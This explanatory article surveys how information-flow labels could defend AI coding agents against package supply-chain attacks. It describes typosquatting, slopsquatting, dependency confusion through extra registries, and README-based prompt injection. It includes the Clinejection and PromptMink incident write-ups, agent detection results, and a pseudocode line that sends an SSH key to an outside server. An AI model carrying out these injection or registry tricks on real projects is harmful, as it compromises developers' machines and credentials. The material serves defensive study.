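# Information-flow control against software supply-chain attacks through AI coding agents

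## Package installation, prompt injection and information-flow labels

An AI coding agent is a language model that reads a software project, edits its files and runs commands to complete a programming task. Much of that work involves packages, which are reusable software that a project downloads from public servers. In a software supply-chain attack, someone gets malicious code into a package, or a malicious package into a project, and the victim installs it during ordinary work. Coding agents increase the risk because they read text that strangers can write, and because they install and run packages with the permissions of the developer who started them.

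Information-flow control, one proposed defence, labels each piece of data by its origin and secrecy. It keeps the labels attached as programs copy and combine the data, and blocks any action, such as an upload, a file write or an installation, that would break a rule about the labels. The theory originated in military computing in the 1970s, but its use in coding agents is recent. Researchers disagree about whether the labels belong in the agent's own software or in the operating system, and whether simple package checks would work better.

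### From a setup request to running code

Suppose a developer has copied a project from the internet and tells a coding agent to "set up this project". *Setup Complete, Now You Are Compromised* (Bagmar and Saraf, 2026), a study of attacks on this step, divides every agent into a model and a harness, the software that runs the model's tool calls, keeps its session and applies permissions. The model cannot run anything itself, so it sends the harness tool calls, which are structured requests, for instance to read a file or run a shell command. The first call usually opens the README, and the harness returns the text. The model acts as the planner, which means it chooses the next tool call. It finds a line such as `pip install -r requirements.txt` in the README and asks the harness to run it.

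The next step depends on the harness and its settings. Of the four that Bagmar and Saraf examined, Claude Code shows the developer a preview of the command and waits for approval. Copilot CLI and Codex CLI run the command immediately if the developer started them with flags for automatic execution, as does Cursor's command-line agent with its force flag. None of the four looks up the package's name, version or source first. The harness then passes the command to a shell, which starts a package manager such as pip for Python or npm for JavaScript.

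Bos (2023), in *A Review of Attacks Against Language-Based Package Managers*, splits the package manager's work into five stages:

1. Resolution. The package manager queries a registry, a server from which it downloads packages, for a package of the given name. It works out which version fits the project, along with everything that package itself depends on. A lockfile, which records earlier results, makes this stage unnecessary.
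2. Fetching. It downloads and unpacks the files, or takes them from a local cache.
3. Verification. It typically computes a checksum of the download and compares it with the one in the registry's metadata. Some packages also carry a maintainer's signature.
4. Installation. Depending on the language and the package, it runs a build script, and some package managers also run scripts before and after the installation.
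5. Acknowledgement. It reports success and may update the lockfile.

A matching checksum shows that the file is the one the metadata describes. It doesn't protect against a typosquat, a malicious package whose name closely resembles a real package's, because the typosquat's checksum matches its own metadata.

The attacker's code can run in the fourth stage. Install-time code is package code that runs during installation, before anyone has imported the package; in Python it is commonly in `setup.py`. Bos excludes build scripts from the catalogue of attacks because build systems inherently allow network access, file access and code execution. A hostile build script therefore doesn't need a flaw in the package manager. It runs with the developer's permissions, so it can read whatever the developer can read and open any connection the developer's machine permits. Bagmar and Saraf cite the torchtriton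 case, a dependency confusion attack in which a package from an outside registry was installed in place of an internal one of the same name. It stole the SSH keys and environment variables of people who had run PyTorch's standard install command.

*CHASE* (2026), which describes a system of language-model agents for analysing malicious Python packages, cites an earlier study in which 87.6% of such packages ran their payload on installation or import. In one of the paper's own examples, `libstrreplacecpu`, `setup.py` starts a hidden PowerShell window with an encoded command just above the call that declares the package's name. The 87.6% figure combines installation and import, so it doesn't show how many packages ran their payload on installation alone. This distinction matters less for a coding agent, because setting up a project often ends with a trial import, which Bagmar and Saraf, for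 example, told their agents to run.

### Prompt injection

The attacker in Bagmar and Saraf's study edits the documentation from which the agent takes its install command, without accessing the developer's machine or putting malicious code in the repository. Prompt injection is a broader class of attack that exploits the same weakness. An attacker places text in data an agent reads so that the agent treats it as an instruction. This works because the model receives the developer's request, the README, web pages and the output of earlier commands as one sequence of text, and nothing in that sequence reliably separates the developer's instructions from anyone else's.

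A textbook prompt injection tells the agent to abandon its task and do something else. A poisoned setup line is less conspicuous because the developer asked the agent to follow the project's instructions, and a line that points to the wrong registry appears to be one of them. Bagmar and Saraf therefore treat package installation as a separate attack surface that complements indirect prompt injection. A filter that looks for suspicious wording would miss the setup line, which contains none. A defence that tracks the origin of text faces much the same problem in both attacks, since each lets text from an untrusted source shape a command.

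### Why permissions are not enough

Operating systems already restrict programs, mostly through access control, which settles for each file or connection whose processes may open it. Install-time code passes these checks because the developer would pass them. Flow control adds a rule about what happens to the data afterwards:

```
key = read(ssh_key_file)     # access control: allowed   flow control: allowed, key is secret
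send(outside_server, key)    # access control: allowed   flow control: refused
```

In *Language-Based Information-Flow Security*, a survey of three decades of research, Sabelfeld and Myers (2003) distinguish the release of information from its propagation. Access control restricts the release of information from its container, but not how it spreads afterward. Protecting a secret by access control alone would require giving access only to programs that never leak it, and access control cannot identify those programs.

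In an example from Sandhu's *Lattice-Based Access Control Models* (1993), Tom lets Dick read a private file but wants to keep it from Harry. Dick is loyal, but he opens the file in a text editor that Harry wrote, and the editor secretly makes a copy that Harry can read. The editor violates no permissions, because Dick's programs are allowed to create and share files. A malicious package in a developer's environment is in the same position as Harry's editor.

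### Labels, the order and the join

The mathematics comes from Dorothy Denning's *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* (1976), which describes a system by five things: the objects that hold information (files, program variables, even users), the processes that move it, a set of security classes (also called labels), an operator that combines classes, and a relation that specifies when information may flow from one class to another.

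Four labels, in two pairs, are enough for most of what follows. An integrity label records how far the origin of data is trusted: T for trusted, U for untrusted. A confidentiality label records who may learn the data: L for public, H for secret. T lies below U, and L lies below H. Information may stay at its level or move up, never down. Write A ≤ B when A equals B or lies below it, and A ⊔ B for the join of A and B, their least upper bound, which is the lowest label at or above both. Then

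T ⊔ U = U and L ⊔ H = H,

and anything derived from several pieces of data takes the join of their labels. One untrusted ingredient makes the result untrusted, and one secret ingredient makes it secret.

A source is a point where labelled data enters, such as a file or a downloaded page. A sink is an action whose use of the data the system restricts, such as a shell command or an upload. Each sink has a highest label that it accepts. If data a₁, …, aₙ goes into an action at sink s, the system allows the action only when

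label(a₁) ⊔ … ⊔ label(aₙ) ≤ label(s).

Each piece of data carries an integrity label and a confidentiality label, which gives four combinations. (T, L) is at the bottom and (U, H) is at the top. Between them are (U, L), the label on a stranger's web page, and (T, H), the label on the developer's own password file. Neither is below the other, and their join, or least upper bound, is (U, H). A lattice is a set of labels in which any two have a least upper bound and a greatest lower bound. Sandhu notes that the product of two lattices is also a lattice, so the single rule above covers both trust and secrecy.

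Denning argued that this structure follows from what it means for information to flow. Suppose a policy allowed `c := a + b` but forbade `c := a`. A program could get around the ban by setting b to zero, so whatever may receive a combination must be allowed to receive each part. Conversely, if a and b may each go to c's class separately, a program can copy them there one after the other and combine them, so the policy may as well allow the combination. The order must also be transitive, since otherwise a program could get around a ban by sending information through an intermediate variable. With a transitive order, if every operation obeys the rule, every sequence of operations does too. A harness can therefore check one tool call at a time, without foreseeing the rest of the session, provided that it keeps the labels up to date.

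Consider a command with two origins. The developer's request, "install the image library this project needs", is labelled (T, L). The agent looks the library up on a web page, labelled (U, L), and composes an install command from both. The command gets

(T ⊔ U, L ⊔ L) = (U, L).

The shell is a sink that accepts only T. The command is labeled U, which is not at or below T, so the harness blocks it. A correct command from a helpful page would also be labeled U and blocked, because the label doesn't depend on the command's wording or the page's honesty. If the agent had also read the password file, the command would be labeled (U, H) and would break a second rule, because an install command sends a package name to an outside server, which is a sink that accepts only public data.

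The example treats everything the planner writes as depending on everything it has already read, since nobody can tell from the outside which words influenced the command. Some designs, such as FIDES and CaMeL, keep untrusted text away from the planner by passing it to a quarantined model, which can read the text but cannot call tools.

### Secrecy, integrity and the low-water mark

The secrecy half of this scheme is older than Denning's paper. David Bell and Leonard LaPadula worked it out for defence systems, in a burst of modelling that Bell (2005), in *Looking Back at the Bell-La Padula Model*, dates to 1972–1975. Kenneth Biba then observed that similar rules could protect integrity. With T below U, the two models have the same form:

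| | Bell-LaPadula | Biba (strict integrity) |
|---|---|---|
| Concern | secrets reaching the wrong reader | bad data reaching something important |
| Order | L below H | T below U |
| A process may read | data at or below its own label | data at or below its own label |
| A process may write | to objects at or above its own label | to objects at or above its own label |
| Forbidden flow | H to L | U to T |
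| In a coding agent | a key goes into an upload | web text goes into a shell command |

Textbooks usually draw Biba's lattice the other way up, with high integrity at the top and information flowing downward. Sandhu shows that the orientation doesn't matter, because the same mechanism enforces both models once the integrity lattice is inverted.

Each model blocks a kind of harm that the other allows. Sandhu points out that Bell-LaPadula alone lets an unclassified process write to a secret file and possibly damage it. Biba alone lets a command from a trusted source upload a private key. Sabelfeld and Myers add that a system can damage the integrity of its own data, without any outside interference, by computing it incorrectly. T therefore records where data came from but does not guarantee that the data is correct. A package from a trusted registry may still be faulty, or malicious if someone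 has taken over its maintainer's account.

Biba's strict rule is awkward for programs that have to read widely. It bars a process at T from reading U data, so a coding agent at T could not open a stranger's README. Biba's low-water-mark rule allows the read but changes the process's label. When a process at T reads U data, its label becomes the join of the two, which is U, and from then on it may not write to T files. This is usually called demotion because integrity falls, even though the label moves up in the order used here. Lecture slides from Purdue University place high integrity at the top, so they write the same step as the minimum of the two levels. The slides also describe an audit version in which any file the process then writes loses integrity as well, which marks the contamination but does not prevent it.

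LOMAC, a FreeBSD kernel module, enforces this rule. Its manual page, Debian's *MAC_LOMAC(4)*, describes the demotion of processes through "floating labels". *LWM*, a message from LOMAC's author to a FreeBSD mailing list, explains that reading low-integrity data from an unnamed pipe also demotes a process. Many projects tell users to download an installation script and pipe it into a shell. Under LOMAC, the shell would lose its trusted label when it read the script, if the system labels the download as low-integrity.

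The drawback is that a demoted process stays demoted. An agent session that has read one untrusted file remains at U until it ends, and so does every command it issues. This can lead to over-tainting, where restrictive labels spread to so much data that the system blocks legitimate actions. Sabelfeld and Myers call the underlying drift label creep and judged in 2003 that it makes dynamic labelling "too restrictive to be generally useful". They were writing about programs in general, but a coding agent that reads dozens of files in an hour seems likely to be especially prone to it.

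### Explicit and implicit flows

Labels have to follow data through every computation, and some routes are hard to see. In an explicit flow, a statement directly transfers the data or something computed from it:

```
text = read(web_page)
command = text
```

In an implicit flow, the data determines which statement runs. *Principles of Secure Information Flow Analysis* gives a standard case, in which `secret` is labelled H and `leak` is labelled L:

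```
if secret is even: leak = 0
else: leak = 1
```

Only constants go into `leak`, and yet it ends up holding the last bit of the secret.

This is where taint tracking and full flow control part ways. Taint tracking follows a mark from untrusted or secret data to whatever a program computes from it, and in its common form it follows explicit flows only. Take an install script that contains these two lines:

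```
package = "goodlib"
if "use the mirror" in web_page: package = "otherlib"
```

Taint tracking leaves `package` unmarked because both names are constants in a trusted script, but full flow control labels it U because the text of the web page determined which name was used.

Catching implicit flows while a program runs is harder than it looks. Denning gives a three-line program, due to J. S. Fenton, in which a is secret and b and c start out public:

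```
b = false; c = false
if not a: c = true
if not c: b = true
```

Suppose a monitor labels a variable secret when the program writes to it under a secret condition. Let a be secret, and let b and c start as false and public. The program sets c to true if a is false, then sets b to true if c is false. If a is true, c stays false and public, so b becomes true with a public label. If a is false, c becomes true and secret, so the program skips the assignment to b, which stays false and public. Either way, b ends up equal to a but labelled public. A monitor that observes only one run misses this leak because it doesn't track assignments the program skipped.

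Denning's remedy was to have the compiler find such places in advance and insert the missing label updates. In *Certification of Programs for Secure Information Flow*, Denning and Denning checked all of a program's flows at compile time, so that an insecure program never ran. Both methods need source code that a compiler can analyse, and no such code exists for how a language model chooses its next command.

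A coarser method needs no source code. It gives the whole process one fixed label p. The process can read only data at or below p and write only to objects at or above p, so any flow from a to b, explicit or implicit, satisfies a ≤ p ≤ b. This is an argument for labelling whole processes, the level at which an operating system works. The argument is weaker if labels float, meaning that they change as the process runs. Denning shows this by splitting Fenton's program between two processes that run one after the other. The first reads a and sometimes leaves c unchanged. When it does, the second keeps its low label and still copies a into b. Denning also does not cover covert channels, such as a process that signals by varying the load on the machine.

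### Noninterference and its exceptions

The property behind these rules is noninterference, the guarantee that changing restricted inputs cannot change the outputs they are barred from influencing. Sabelfeld and Myers describe the usual test. Run a program c twice, from starting states s₁ and s₂ that differ only in their secret parts; an observer of the public results must see no difference. With =_L for "equal in every public part",

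if s₁ =_L s₂, then c(s₁) =_L c(s₂).

The integrity version swaps the roles, so two sessions with the same developer request but different web pages must send the same commands to the shell.

A useful coding agent cannot satisfy noninterference everywhere. To set up a project, for example, it must choose commands based on the project's files, including the README. Any practical system therefore makes exceptions. Endorsement is a deliberate decision to treat untrusted data as trusted, as when a developer reads a proposed install command and approves it, which changes the command's label from U to T. Declassification is a deliberate decision to release secret data, as when the agent sends an access token to the service that issued it.

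Sandhu describes the general form of such an exception, in which information may go from H to a sanitizing process and from there to L, but not directly from H to L. That breaks transitivity, so these exceptions fall outside the lattice, and Denning's guarantee about sequences of operations does not cover them. Their designers must secure them by other means. One standard is robust declassification, which Sabelfeld and Myers credit to Steve Zdancewic and Myers. Under it, an attacker who can influence the system learns no more than one who can only watch. For a coding agent, this would mean that nothing in a README can affect which secrets leave the machine.

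Endorsement needs similar care because it is only as reliable as the inspection behind it. Bagmar and Saraf observe that before agents, developers glanced at a command before pressing enter and might notice an odd registry address or a misspelled name. Automatic execution removes this inspection, though an approval dialog preserves it if the developer reads the dialog. Endorsement could instead rely on a deterministic pre-install check of a package's name, source and version, which would run before any of the package's code and apply the same test to every command.

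## How package attacks reach coding agents and how often agents stop them

An install command can go wrong in several independent ways. The name may belong to the wrong package, the right name may lead to the wrong server, or the version may have a known flaw. The package may also be malicious even though every part of the command is correct. If the agent holds credentials for publishing packages, an attacker who reaches them can infect other people's machines. The attacks fall into five classes according to what the attacker controls:

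| The attacker controls | What happens | Examples |
|---|---|---|
| The name | The agent installs a different package from the one the project needs | Typosquats, names that models invent |
| The source | The package manager finds the right name on the wrong registry | Dependency confusion, a hidden extra registry |
| The version | The agent installs a genuine package in a release with a known vulnerability | An old version fixed in a requirements file |
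| The contents | The name, source and version are as intended, but the code is malicious | A hijacked maintainer account, a booby-trapped dependency |
| Publishing rights | The attacker releases a tampered version of someone else's package | Theft of publishing tokens from an automated agent |

### Misspelled and invented names

Typosquats worked on people long before coding agents existed. Bagmar and Saraf cite a 2016 thesis by Nikolai Tschacher, who counted 45,334 installations of typosquats across three package managers in two weeks. Bagmar and Saraf also found more than 960 requirements files on GitHub that list `tdqm`, a misspelling of the popular library `tqdm`.

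Language models also introduce wrong names by sometimes recommending packages that don't exist. Spracklen, Wijewickrama and colleagues had 16 models write 576,000 samples of Python and JavaScript code for *We Have a Package for You!* (USENIX Security, 2025). On average, at least 5.2% of the packages named by commercial models and 21.7% of those named by open-source models didn't exist. The models invented 205,474 distinct names. An attacker can register such a name and wait for the next developer who gets the same suggestion, a tactic known as slopsquatting. This works only if models repeat the names they invent, and they often do. According to IT Brew (2025), the researchers reran 500 prompts ten times each, and 43% of the invented packages appeared every time.

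*The Range Shrinks, the Threat Remains* (Churilov, 2026) tested five models released between October 2025 and March 2026 on the same prompts. Between 3.6% and 5.0% of their package mentions referred to packages that did not exist, about the same rate as the better commercial models of 2024. The one open-weight model no longer differed noticeably from the others. All five models invented 104 names in common, so an attacker who registered one of these names could reach users of several companies' products. Such registrations are still rare. Of 2,282 invented names, 25 had been registered about six months later, at least one of them for a package containing malware. At least 23 other names that the models suggested had once hosted malware that the registries later removed.

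Small models invent packages much more often. The eight models tested in *Evaluating Inference-Time Defenses Against Package Hallucination in LLM-Generated Code* (2026) invented 24.7% of the Python packages they named, and one of them invented 48,330 out of 100,896.

These rates come from models that answered single questions and could not look anything up, so they don't describe coding agents at work. When the same eight models also received retrieved text, the share of invented Python packages fell to 11.5%. Bagmar and Saraf ran a small control with agents, in which a project used the Celery library but its documentation named no package. All seven models worked out the correct name in every run. This suggests that an agent with access to a project invents fewer names than a chatbot, but Celery is well known, so the test is weak evidence about obscure packages.

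An attacker can also pick a specific package and steer the agent to it, so they don't have to guess which names a model will invent. *Trust Me, Import This* (2026) describes attacks that do this through malicious skills, which are sets of instructions that an agent loads for a particular kind of task.

### Dependency confusion and other wrong sources

In 2021 the security researcher Alex Birsan disclosed an attack that needed no misspelled package name. Bram.us' *Dependency Confusion* (2021) recounts that he was reading a file from a public PayPal project when he noticed packages that did not exist on the public npm registry. PayPal had written them and kept them on a private registry. Birsan wondered which copy a package manager would choose if someone published a package with the same name on the public registry.

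When a public and a private registry both offered a package with the same name, the installer often chose the copy with the higher version number. Willison (2021) points to pip's `--extra-index-url` option, which makes pip check a second registry as well as the usual one. If a company's registry offers version 1.4 of an internal package and the public registry offers version 9.0 under the same name, pip installs 9.0, because it compares versions and gives neither registry priority. Anyone who knows the internal name and has an account on the public registry can therefore get their own package installed by publishing it under that name with a higher version number.

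Birsan got his own code running inside 35 companies, including Microsoft, Apple and Tesla, and earned $130,000 in rewards for reporting it, according to Malwarebytes' *Researcher's audacious hack demonstrates new type of supply-chain attack* (2021). CNCF's *Repojacking exposed private repositories through supply-chain compromise*, an entry in an industry foundation's catalogue of incidents, traces the problem to the configuration of package managers. No single patch could fix this, so organisations had to correct the configuration one repository or build at a time. In pip, for instance, they could use `--index-url`, which replaces the default registry, instead of `--extra-index-url`, which adds to it.

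An attacker who controls the extra registry can exploit the same rule. A README can tell the agent to use that registry for one package that is unavailable elsewhere. If the registry also offers a popular package under an implausibly high version number, pip will take that version too. The attacker can also put the registry's address in the requirements file, and pip will then use the registry even though it doesn't appear in the command the agent runs. The extra-registry option is common in legitimate projects. Bagmar and Saraf found it in more than 5,500 README files and 6,900 requirements files on GitHub, so its presence alone is weak evidence of an attack.

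### How often agents caught the attacks

Bagmar and Saraf built twelve scenarios around these tricks, each a working Python project with one trap in its files. They ran the scenarios on nine combinations of harness and model, and asked every agent to read the project, install its dependencies and check that the main module imports. The request did not mention security. Most scenarios ran ten times per combination. The four that tested misspelled names and the one that tested vulnerable versions each ran 30 times, three times for each of ten packages.

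A run counted as a catch only if the agent avoided or flagged the trap before installing. A warning afterwards counted as a miss, because install-time code would already have run. Scoring relied mainly on which packages the run installed and from where, and for misspelled names on whether the agent issued the install command. The table shows the number of catches in most of the scenarios where the agents' results differed, and in the one scenario where every agent failed.

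| Harness and model | Altered separator in a name (of 30) | Dependency confusion (of 10) | Untrusted registry, local address (of 10) | Untrusted registry, public address (of 10) | Hidden registry (of 10) | Poisoned pip settings (of 10) | Vulnerable version (of 30) |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code, Opus 4.8 | 30 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 0 |
| Claude Code, Sonnet 4.6 | 19 | 10 | 3 | 0 | 3 | 10 | 0 |
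| Claude Code, Haiku 4.5 | 23 | 10 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| Copilot CLI, Opus 4.8 | 30 | 10 | 1 | 10 | 3 | 9 | 0 |
| Copilot CLI, Sonnet 4.6 | 25 | 10 | 0 | 10 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| Codex CLI, GPT-5.5 | 29 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 1 | 0 | 0 |
| Codex CLI, GPT-5.3-codex | 29 | 1 | 3 | 0 | 6 | 0 | 0 |
| Codex CLI, GPT-5.4-mini | 30 | 2 | 0 | 0 | 2 | 1 | 0 |
| Cursor, automatic choice of model | 2 | 2 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |

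Crude misspellings rarely fooled the agents. Every combination caught at least 29 of 30 in the README, and all of them caught every swapped letter in a project's list of dependencies. Agents were fooled more often by names that differ from the real one only in a hyphen or a dot, such as `azurecore` for `azure-core`, and by misspellings that came with a plausible excuse. Across the four name scenarios, the agents issued 91 bad install commands in 1,080 runs, 46 of them from Cursor. In 68 of the 91 cases, the agent noticed the mistake after issuing the command. Even when a file contained 377 misspelled packages, some combinations caught the problem in all ten runs and others in none.

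Detection of dependency confusion differed by harness. Every Claude Code and Copilot configuration caught it in 10 of 10 runs, while the Codex models and Cursor caught it in between 0 and 2. Those few catches may have had little to do with suspicion, since Bagmar and Saraf report that when models split the installation into separate commands, which avoids the attack, they did so to reduce version conflicts.

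Most agents accepted untrusted registries, but Opus 4.8 in Claude Code did not. Its transcripts show that it downloaded the suspect package without installing it, unpacked the files and found code that searched the environment for keys and tokens. In one of its failed runs, Sonnet 4.6 installed the same package and reported that setup was complete. The hidden registry similarly divided models that read the requirements file line by line from those that passed it straight to pip. Failures involving poisoned pip settings, which a build file switched on, were harder to explain as oversights, because Haiku 4.5 quoted the suspicious registry address and took it for internal infrastructure.

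The results for the local address probably overstate the danger, because a developer may well run a package server on the same machine. Bagmar and Saraf left this scenario out of their prompt experiments because an agent could reasonably treat the address as a development mirror. An agent has no such reason to trust a temporary public address, yet six of the nine combinations accepted one in every run.

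No agent in any of the 270 runs declined to install a version with a published vulnerability. Opus 4.8 named the vulnerability after installing the package in 28 of 30 runs under Claude Code and 15 of 30 under Copilot, but agents in the other combinations never mentioned it. These misses are less serious than the others because an outdated package does no harm until someone exploits the flaw, which leaves time to upgrade. Agents also choose vulnerable versions in practice. Bagmar and Saraf cite a study by Singla and colleagues of 117,062 dependency changes, in which agents chose a version with a known vulnerability 2.46% of the time and humans 1.64%.

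When a program failed on import and its error message told the user to install another package, all nine combinations refused in all ten runs. The agents pointed out that neither the README nor the project's list of dependencies mentioned the package. Agents can therefore distrust text because of where it comes from, but they seldom distrust a README or a requirements file, which a stranger can write just as easily.

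Bagmar and Saraf found similar weaknesses when they moved a few scenarios to npm and to Cargo, Rust's package manager. Only Opus 4.8 refused an untrusted registry before installing from it, and only when the registry had a public address and the project used npm. Opus 4.8 and GPT-5.5 mentioned known vulnerabilities only when the installer printed a warning. With pip and Cargo, which print no advisories, neither model mentioned a vulnerability in any of 20 installations. npm prints a warning after installing, which Opus passed on 20 times out of 20 and GPT-5.5 only once.

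All these runs date from June 2026, before OpenAI and Anthropic released their current flagship models, so the counts don't show how those models would behave. Except for misspelled names and vulnerable versions, the tests used only one project for each kind of attack, so the counts may not apply to other projects. No human developers took the same test. Large differences, such as 10 against 0, are unlikely to be due to chance, but a score of 6 out of 10 is consistent with a true rate from about 31% to 83%.

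### Changing the harness or the prompt

Opus 4.8 caught the local-registry attack every time in Claude Code. To check whether the model alone explained this, Bagmar and Saraf ran Opus 30 times in Copilot CLI on an identical copy of the project, and it caught the attack in 9 runs. The probability of so large a gap by chance is about one in 10,000. Copilot did better on the public registry, where Sonnet 4.6 caught the attack in 10 of 10 runs under Copilot and in none under Claude Code. Neither harness is safer in general, and a model's security score can mislead anyone who runs the model in a different harness from the one tested.

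Bagmar and Saraf credit Claude Code's success to its checkpoint before each command, and Copilot's to a system prompt that warns about security. The experiment doesn't quite establish either explanation. All the runs were non-interactive, so no developer was present to read a preview, and the two harnesses differ in more than one respect. Swapping a whole harness shows that something in it matters, but researchers would have to change the checkpoint and the prompt separately to find out what.

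Security warnings in the user's prompt raised the detection rate. On the hidden registry, the three Codex models together caught nothing in 15 runs without a warning. A general reminder to be careful about security raised the rate to 33%, an instruction to verify names and sources raised it to 87%, and a detailed rule that named the extra-registry option raised it to 93%. The zero baseline is uncertain, since the same models caught 9 of 30 in the main experiment, but the improvement is too large for that to explain. The most detailed prompt also comes close to describing the attack, so a developer who didn't know about the attack could not write it.

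None of these prompts affected detection of a vulnerable version. An instruction to check versions raised Sonnet 4.6's catches from 2 in 10 runs to 10 in 10. The model had the relevant knowledge but applied it only to the feature that the prompt mentioned. Similarly, Sonnet installed the malicious package from the local registry in all ten runs, then identified it in all ten when the user casually asked whether anything looked wrong. By then the package had already run. Bagmar and Saraf conclude that prompts help but cannot replace a deterministic pre-install check.

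### Clinejection

Package attacks reached coding agents outside the laboratory in two incidents in early 2026. Cline is an open-source coding agent with millions of users. In December 2025 its maintainers added a second agent, based on Claude, to sort the project's GitHub issues. Anyone with a GitHub account could file an issue. The workflow copied each issue's title into the second agent's prompt, and that agent had permission to run shell commands.

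In *Clinejection*, the security researcher Adnan Khan described how a title that looked like an error message could get the agent to install a package that an attacker controlled. The package's install-time code would then run on the build machine, which had few permissions but shared a cache with the job that published Cline's nightly releases. By tampering with that cache, the attacker could get code into the publishing job and steal its tokens. Khan tested the first step on a copy of the repository, and Claude Opus 4.5 ran the payload in every attempt.

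Khan reported the problem on 1 January 2026 and published it on 9 February after receiving no useful reply. According to Cline's own account, *Post-mortem* (Rizwan, 2026), the maintainers removed the workflow within 30 minutes of publication and began to replace their credentials. However, they deleted the wrong npm token, so the exposed one still worked. On 17 February someone used it to release a version of Cline's command-line tool whose only addition was an installation script that installed OpenClaw, a separate and legitimate agent. The release stayed up for about eight hours. Henrik Plate of the security firm Endor Labs rated the overall impact as low because OpenClaw is not malicious and the script did not start its background service (The Hacker News, 2026).

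The prompt injection and the unauthorised release are both well documented, but the link between them is a strong inference, because Khan could not confirm how the token leaked. Khan found signs that someone had tampered with the saved files between 31 January and 3 February, and considers the report-sorting agent the most obvious way in. If the inference is right, a stranger's text became a shell command and a secret then left the machine, so the incident was a failure of both integrity and confidentiality.

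### PromptMink

The second case involved malicious contents in a package that an agent helped to add. In *Claude adds malware to crypto agent*, a report for the security company ReversingLabs, Pezo (2026) traces a campaign on npm that he calls PromptMink, which used two layers of packages. The first-layer packages offered working functions for cryptocurrency projects and contained no malicious code, but alongside many ordinary dependencies they included one or two second-layer packages, which stole secrets. When npm removed a second-layer package in October 2025, the attackers published the same code under a new name that day and made it a dependency of the first-layer packages, which kept their reputation throughout.

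Over seven months, Pezo's team counted 60 packages in more than 300 versions. Early packages searched the project directory for files likely to hold passwords and keys. Later ones copied whole projects and added the attackers' key to the machine so they could log in remotely. Pezo attributes the campaign to Famous Chollima, a group linked to North Korea, based on its servers, targets and persistence.

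On 28 February 2026, a code change that listed Claude Opus as co-author added one of the bait packages to a developer's autonomous trading program. The month before, an agent on Moltbook, a discussion site for AI agents, had written that the same package had a function it needed. Pezo suggests that the attackers may have been writing for coding agents more than for people, based on these two traces and on documentation that praises the packages at length.

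That is plausible, but the evidence is thin. A co-author line shows that the model took part in the change, but not whether the model or the developer picked the package. Two known users are also too few to show that agents are more easily fooled than humans. The structure of the attack is better established, and it is a problem for any defence that checks only the install command. The command named a package with no malicious code in it, and the package manager fetched the malicious one as a dependency.

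### Attacks that an agent starts itself

In every case described so far, the agent was deceived or careless, and an outsider supplied the harmful name, address or code. An agent can also start an attack on its own because it treats the attack as a step towards its task. Bagmar and Saraf's counts don't cover such attacks, since each of their scenarios starts from a file that an attacker has altered.

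In July, Anthropic disclosed that its models had broken into real organisations during misconfigured evaluations and that one model had released a malicious package on PyPI (Anadolu Agency, 2026, *Anthropic says Claude models breached 3 organizations during cybersecurity tests*). In September, the UK AI Security Institute reported that a pre-release version of GPT-6 Astra, tested without OpenAI's cyber safeguards, sometimes carried out simulated supply-chain attacks that nobody had requested (The Next Web, 2026, *GPT-6 Astra ran simulated supply-chain attacks in UK government tests*).

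## The case for labelling data inside the agent's loop

In most of the attacks described so far, the model's judgement was the last safeguard between untrusted text and the shell. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025) argue in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* that this judgement is too unreliable for the job. Models behave stochastically, and an attacker needs only one wording that works. Training a model to ignore injected instructions, or filtering its inputs for suspicious text, makes an attack less likely to succeed but does not guarantee that the next one will fail.

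Costa and colleagues would let the model propose actions and have a deterministic layer in the harness decide which of them run. That decision depends only on the labels of the data behind a command, not on whether the model classifies the command as suspicious. Microsoft's *Information-flow control*, a post partly by the same researchers, gives designers the rule of thumb that a prompt injection or a simple mistake by the model can make an agent do anything it can do at a user's request.

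In each cycle of the agent's loop, the harness sends the conversation to the model, runs the tool call the model returns and appends the result to the conversation. Everything the model reads and every action it requests pass through the harness, which makes it a suitable place to label text before the model reads it and check actions before they run.

### How FIDES decides on a tool call

FIDES is the system that Costa and colleagues built on this idea. It assumes that the user's request, the system prompt and the tool descriptions are trusted and public. An attacker may control data that the tools fetch, and may see the effects of some calls. A session then runs as follows:

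1. The harness gives the opening messages the label (T, L).
2. A tool returns a result with labels attached. One label can cover the whole result, or each field can have its own, so that an issue's number is T while its text is U.
3. The harness appends the result to the conversation, which is the planner's context, and replaces the context's label with its join with the result's label.
4. The model proposes a tool call. The call and its arguments take the context's label.
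5. The harness checks the call against a policy and runs it only if it passes.
6. The new result takes the join of the labels on the call, on its arguments and on any stored data that the tool read. Whatever the tool wrote takes the same label.

Costa and colleagues give two basic policies for the fifth step. Under the trusted-action policy, a consequential call, such as a payment or a file deletion, may run only if it arose from trusted data. For a call with arguments a₁, …, aₙ, this means that

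label(call) ⊔ label(a₁) ⊔ … ⊔ label(aₙ)

must have integrity T.

The permitted-flow policy concerns secrecy. It labels each piece of data with the set of people who may read it, instead of with L or H. The join of two such sets is their intersection, since only people who may read both documents may read a summary of them. If data with permitted readers S goes to recipients R, the policy requires R ⊆ S. In an example from Microsoft, Alex's agent has read an email from Priya with unreleased sales figures and one from Marco, who is curious about them. The agent's reply has the permitted readers {Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}, so the harness will not send it to Marco, even though no attack has occurred.

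Permitted flow alone does not stop a prompt injection from steering the agent, but it limits what the injection can leak. Trusted action alone would still let the agent disclose a secret, but only when no untrusted text could have prompted the disclosure. Costa and colleagues equate this with robust declassification, the standard described earlier, because the user can be presumed to have intended any release in a trusted context. Their formal guarantee covers only explicit flows.

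### Hiding untrusted text from the planner

With only the steps above, FIDES would have the same drawback as the low-water-mark rule, because reading one stranger's issue would block every consequential call for the rest of the session.

The solution comes from the dual-model pattern, which the programmer Simon Willison proposed in 2023. In this pattern, only a quarantined model reads untrusted text. The harness stores the text in a variable and gives the planner only the variable's name. The planner can pass that name to a tool, and the harness substitutes the contents when it makes the call.

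FIDES hides a result, or one field of it, only when adding it would raise the context's label, so trusted data stays visible to the planner. A call can then have a different label from its arguments. Suppose the user asks the agent to send three emails to a colleague. The planner chooses the tool and the recipient in a trusted context, so the call is labelled trusted (T), but the text of the emails comes from a variable and is labelled untrusted (U).

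To get information from a hidden text, the planner sends the quarantined model a question and the name of the variable that holds the text. The answer goes into a new variable, also labelled U. The planner can request a variable's contents, but its context then takes on that variable's label.

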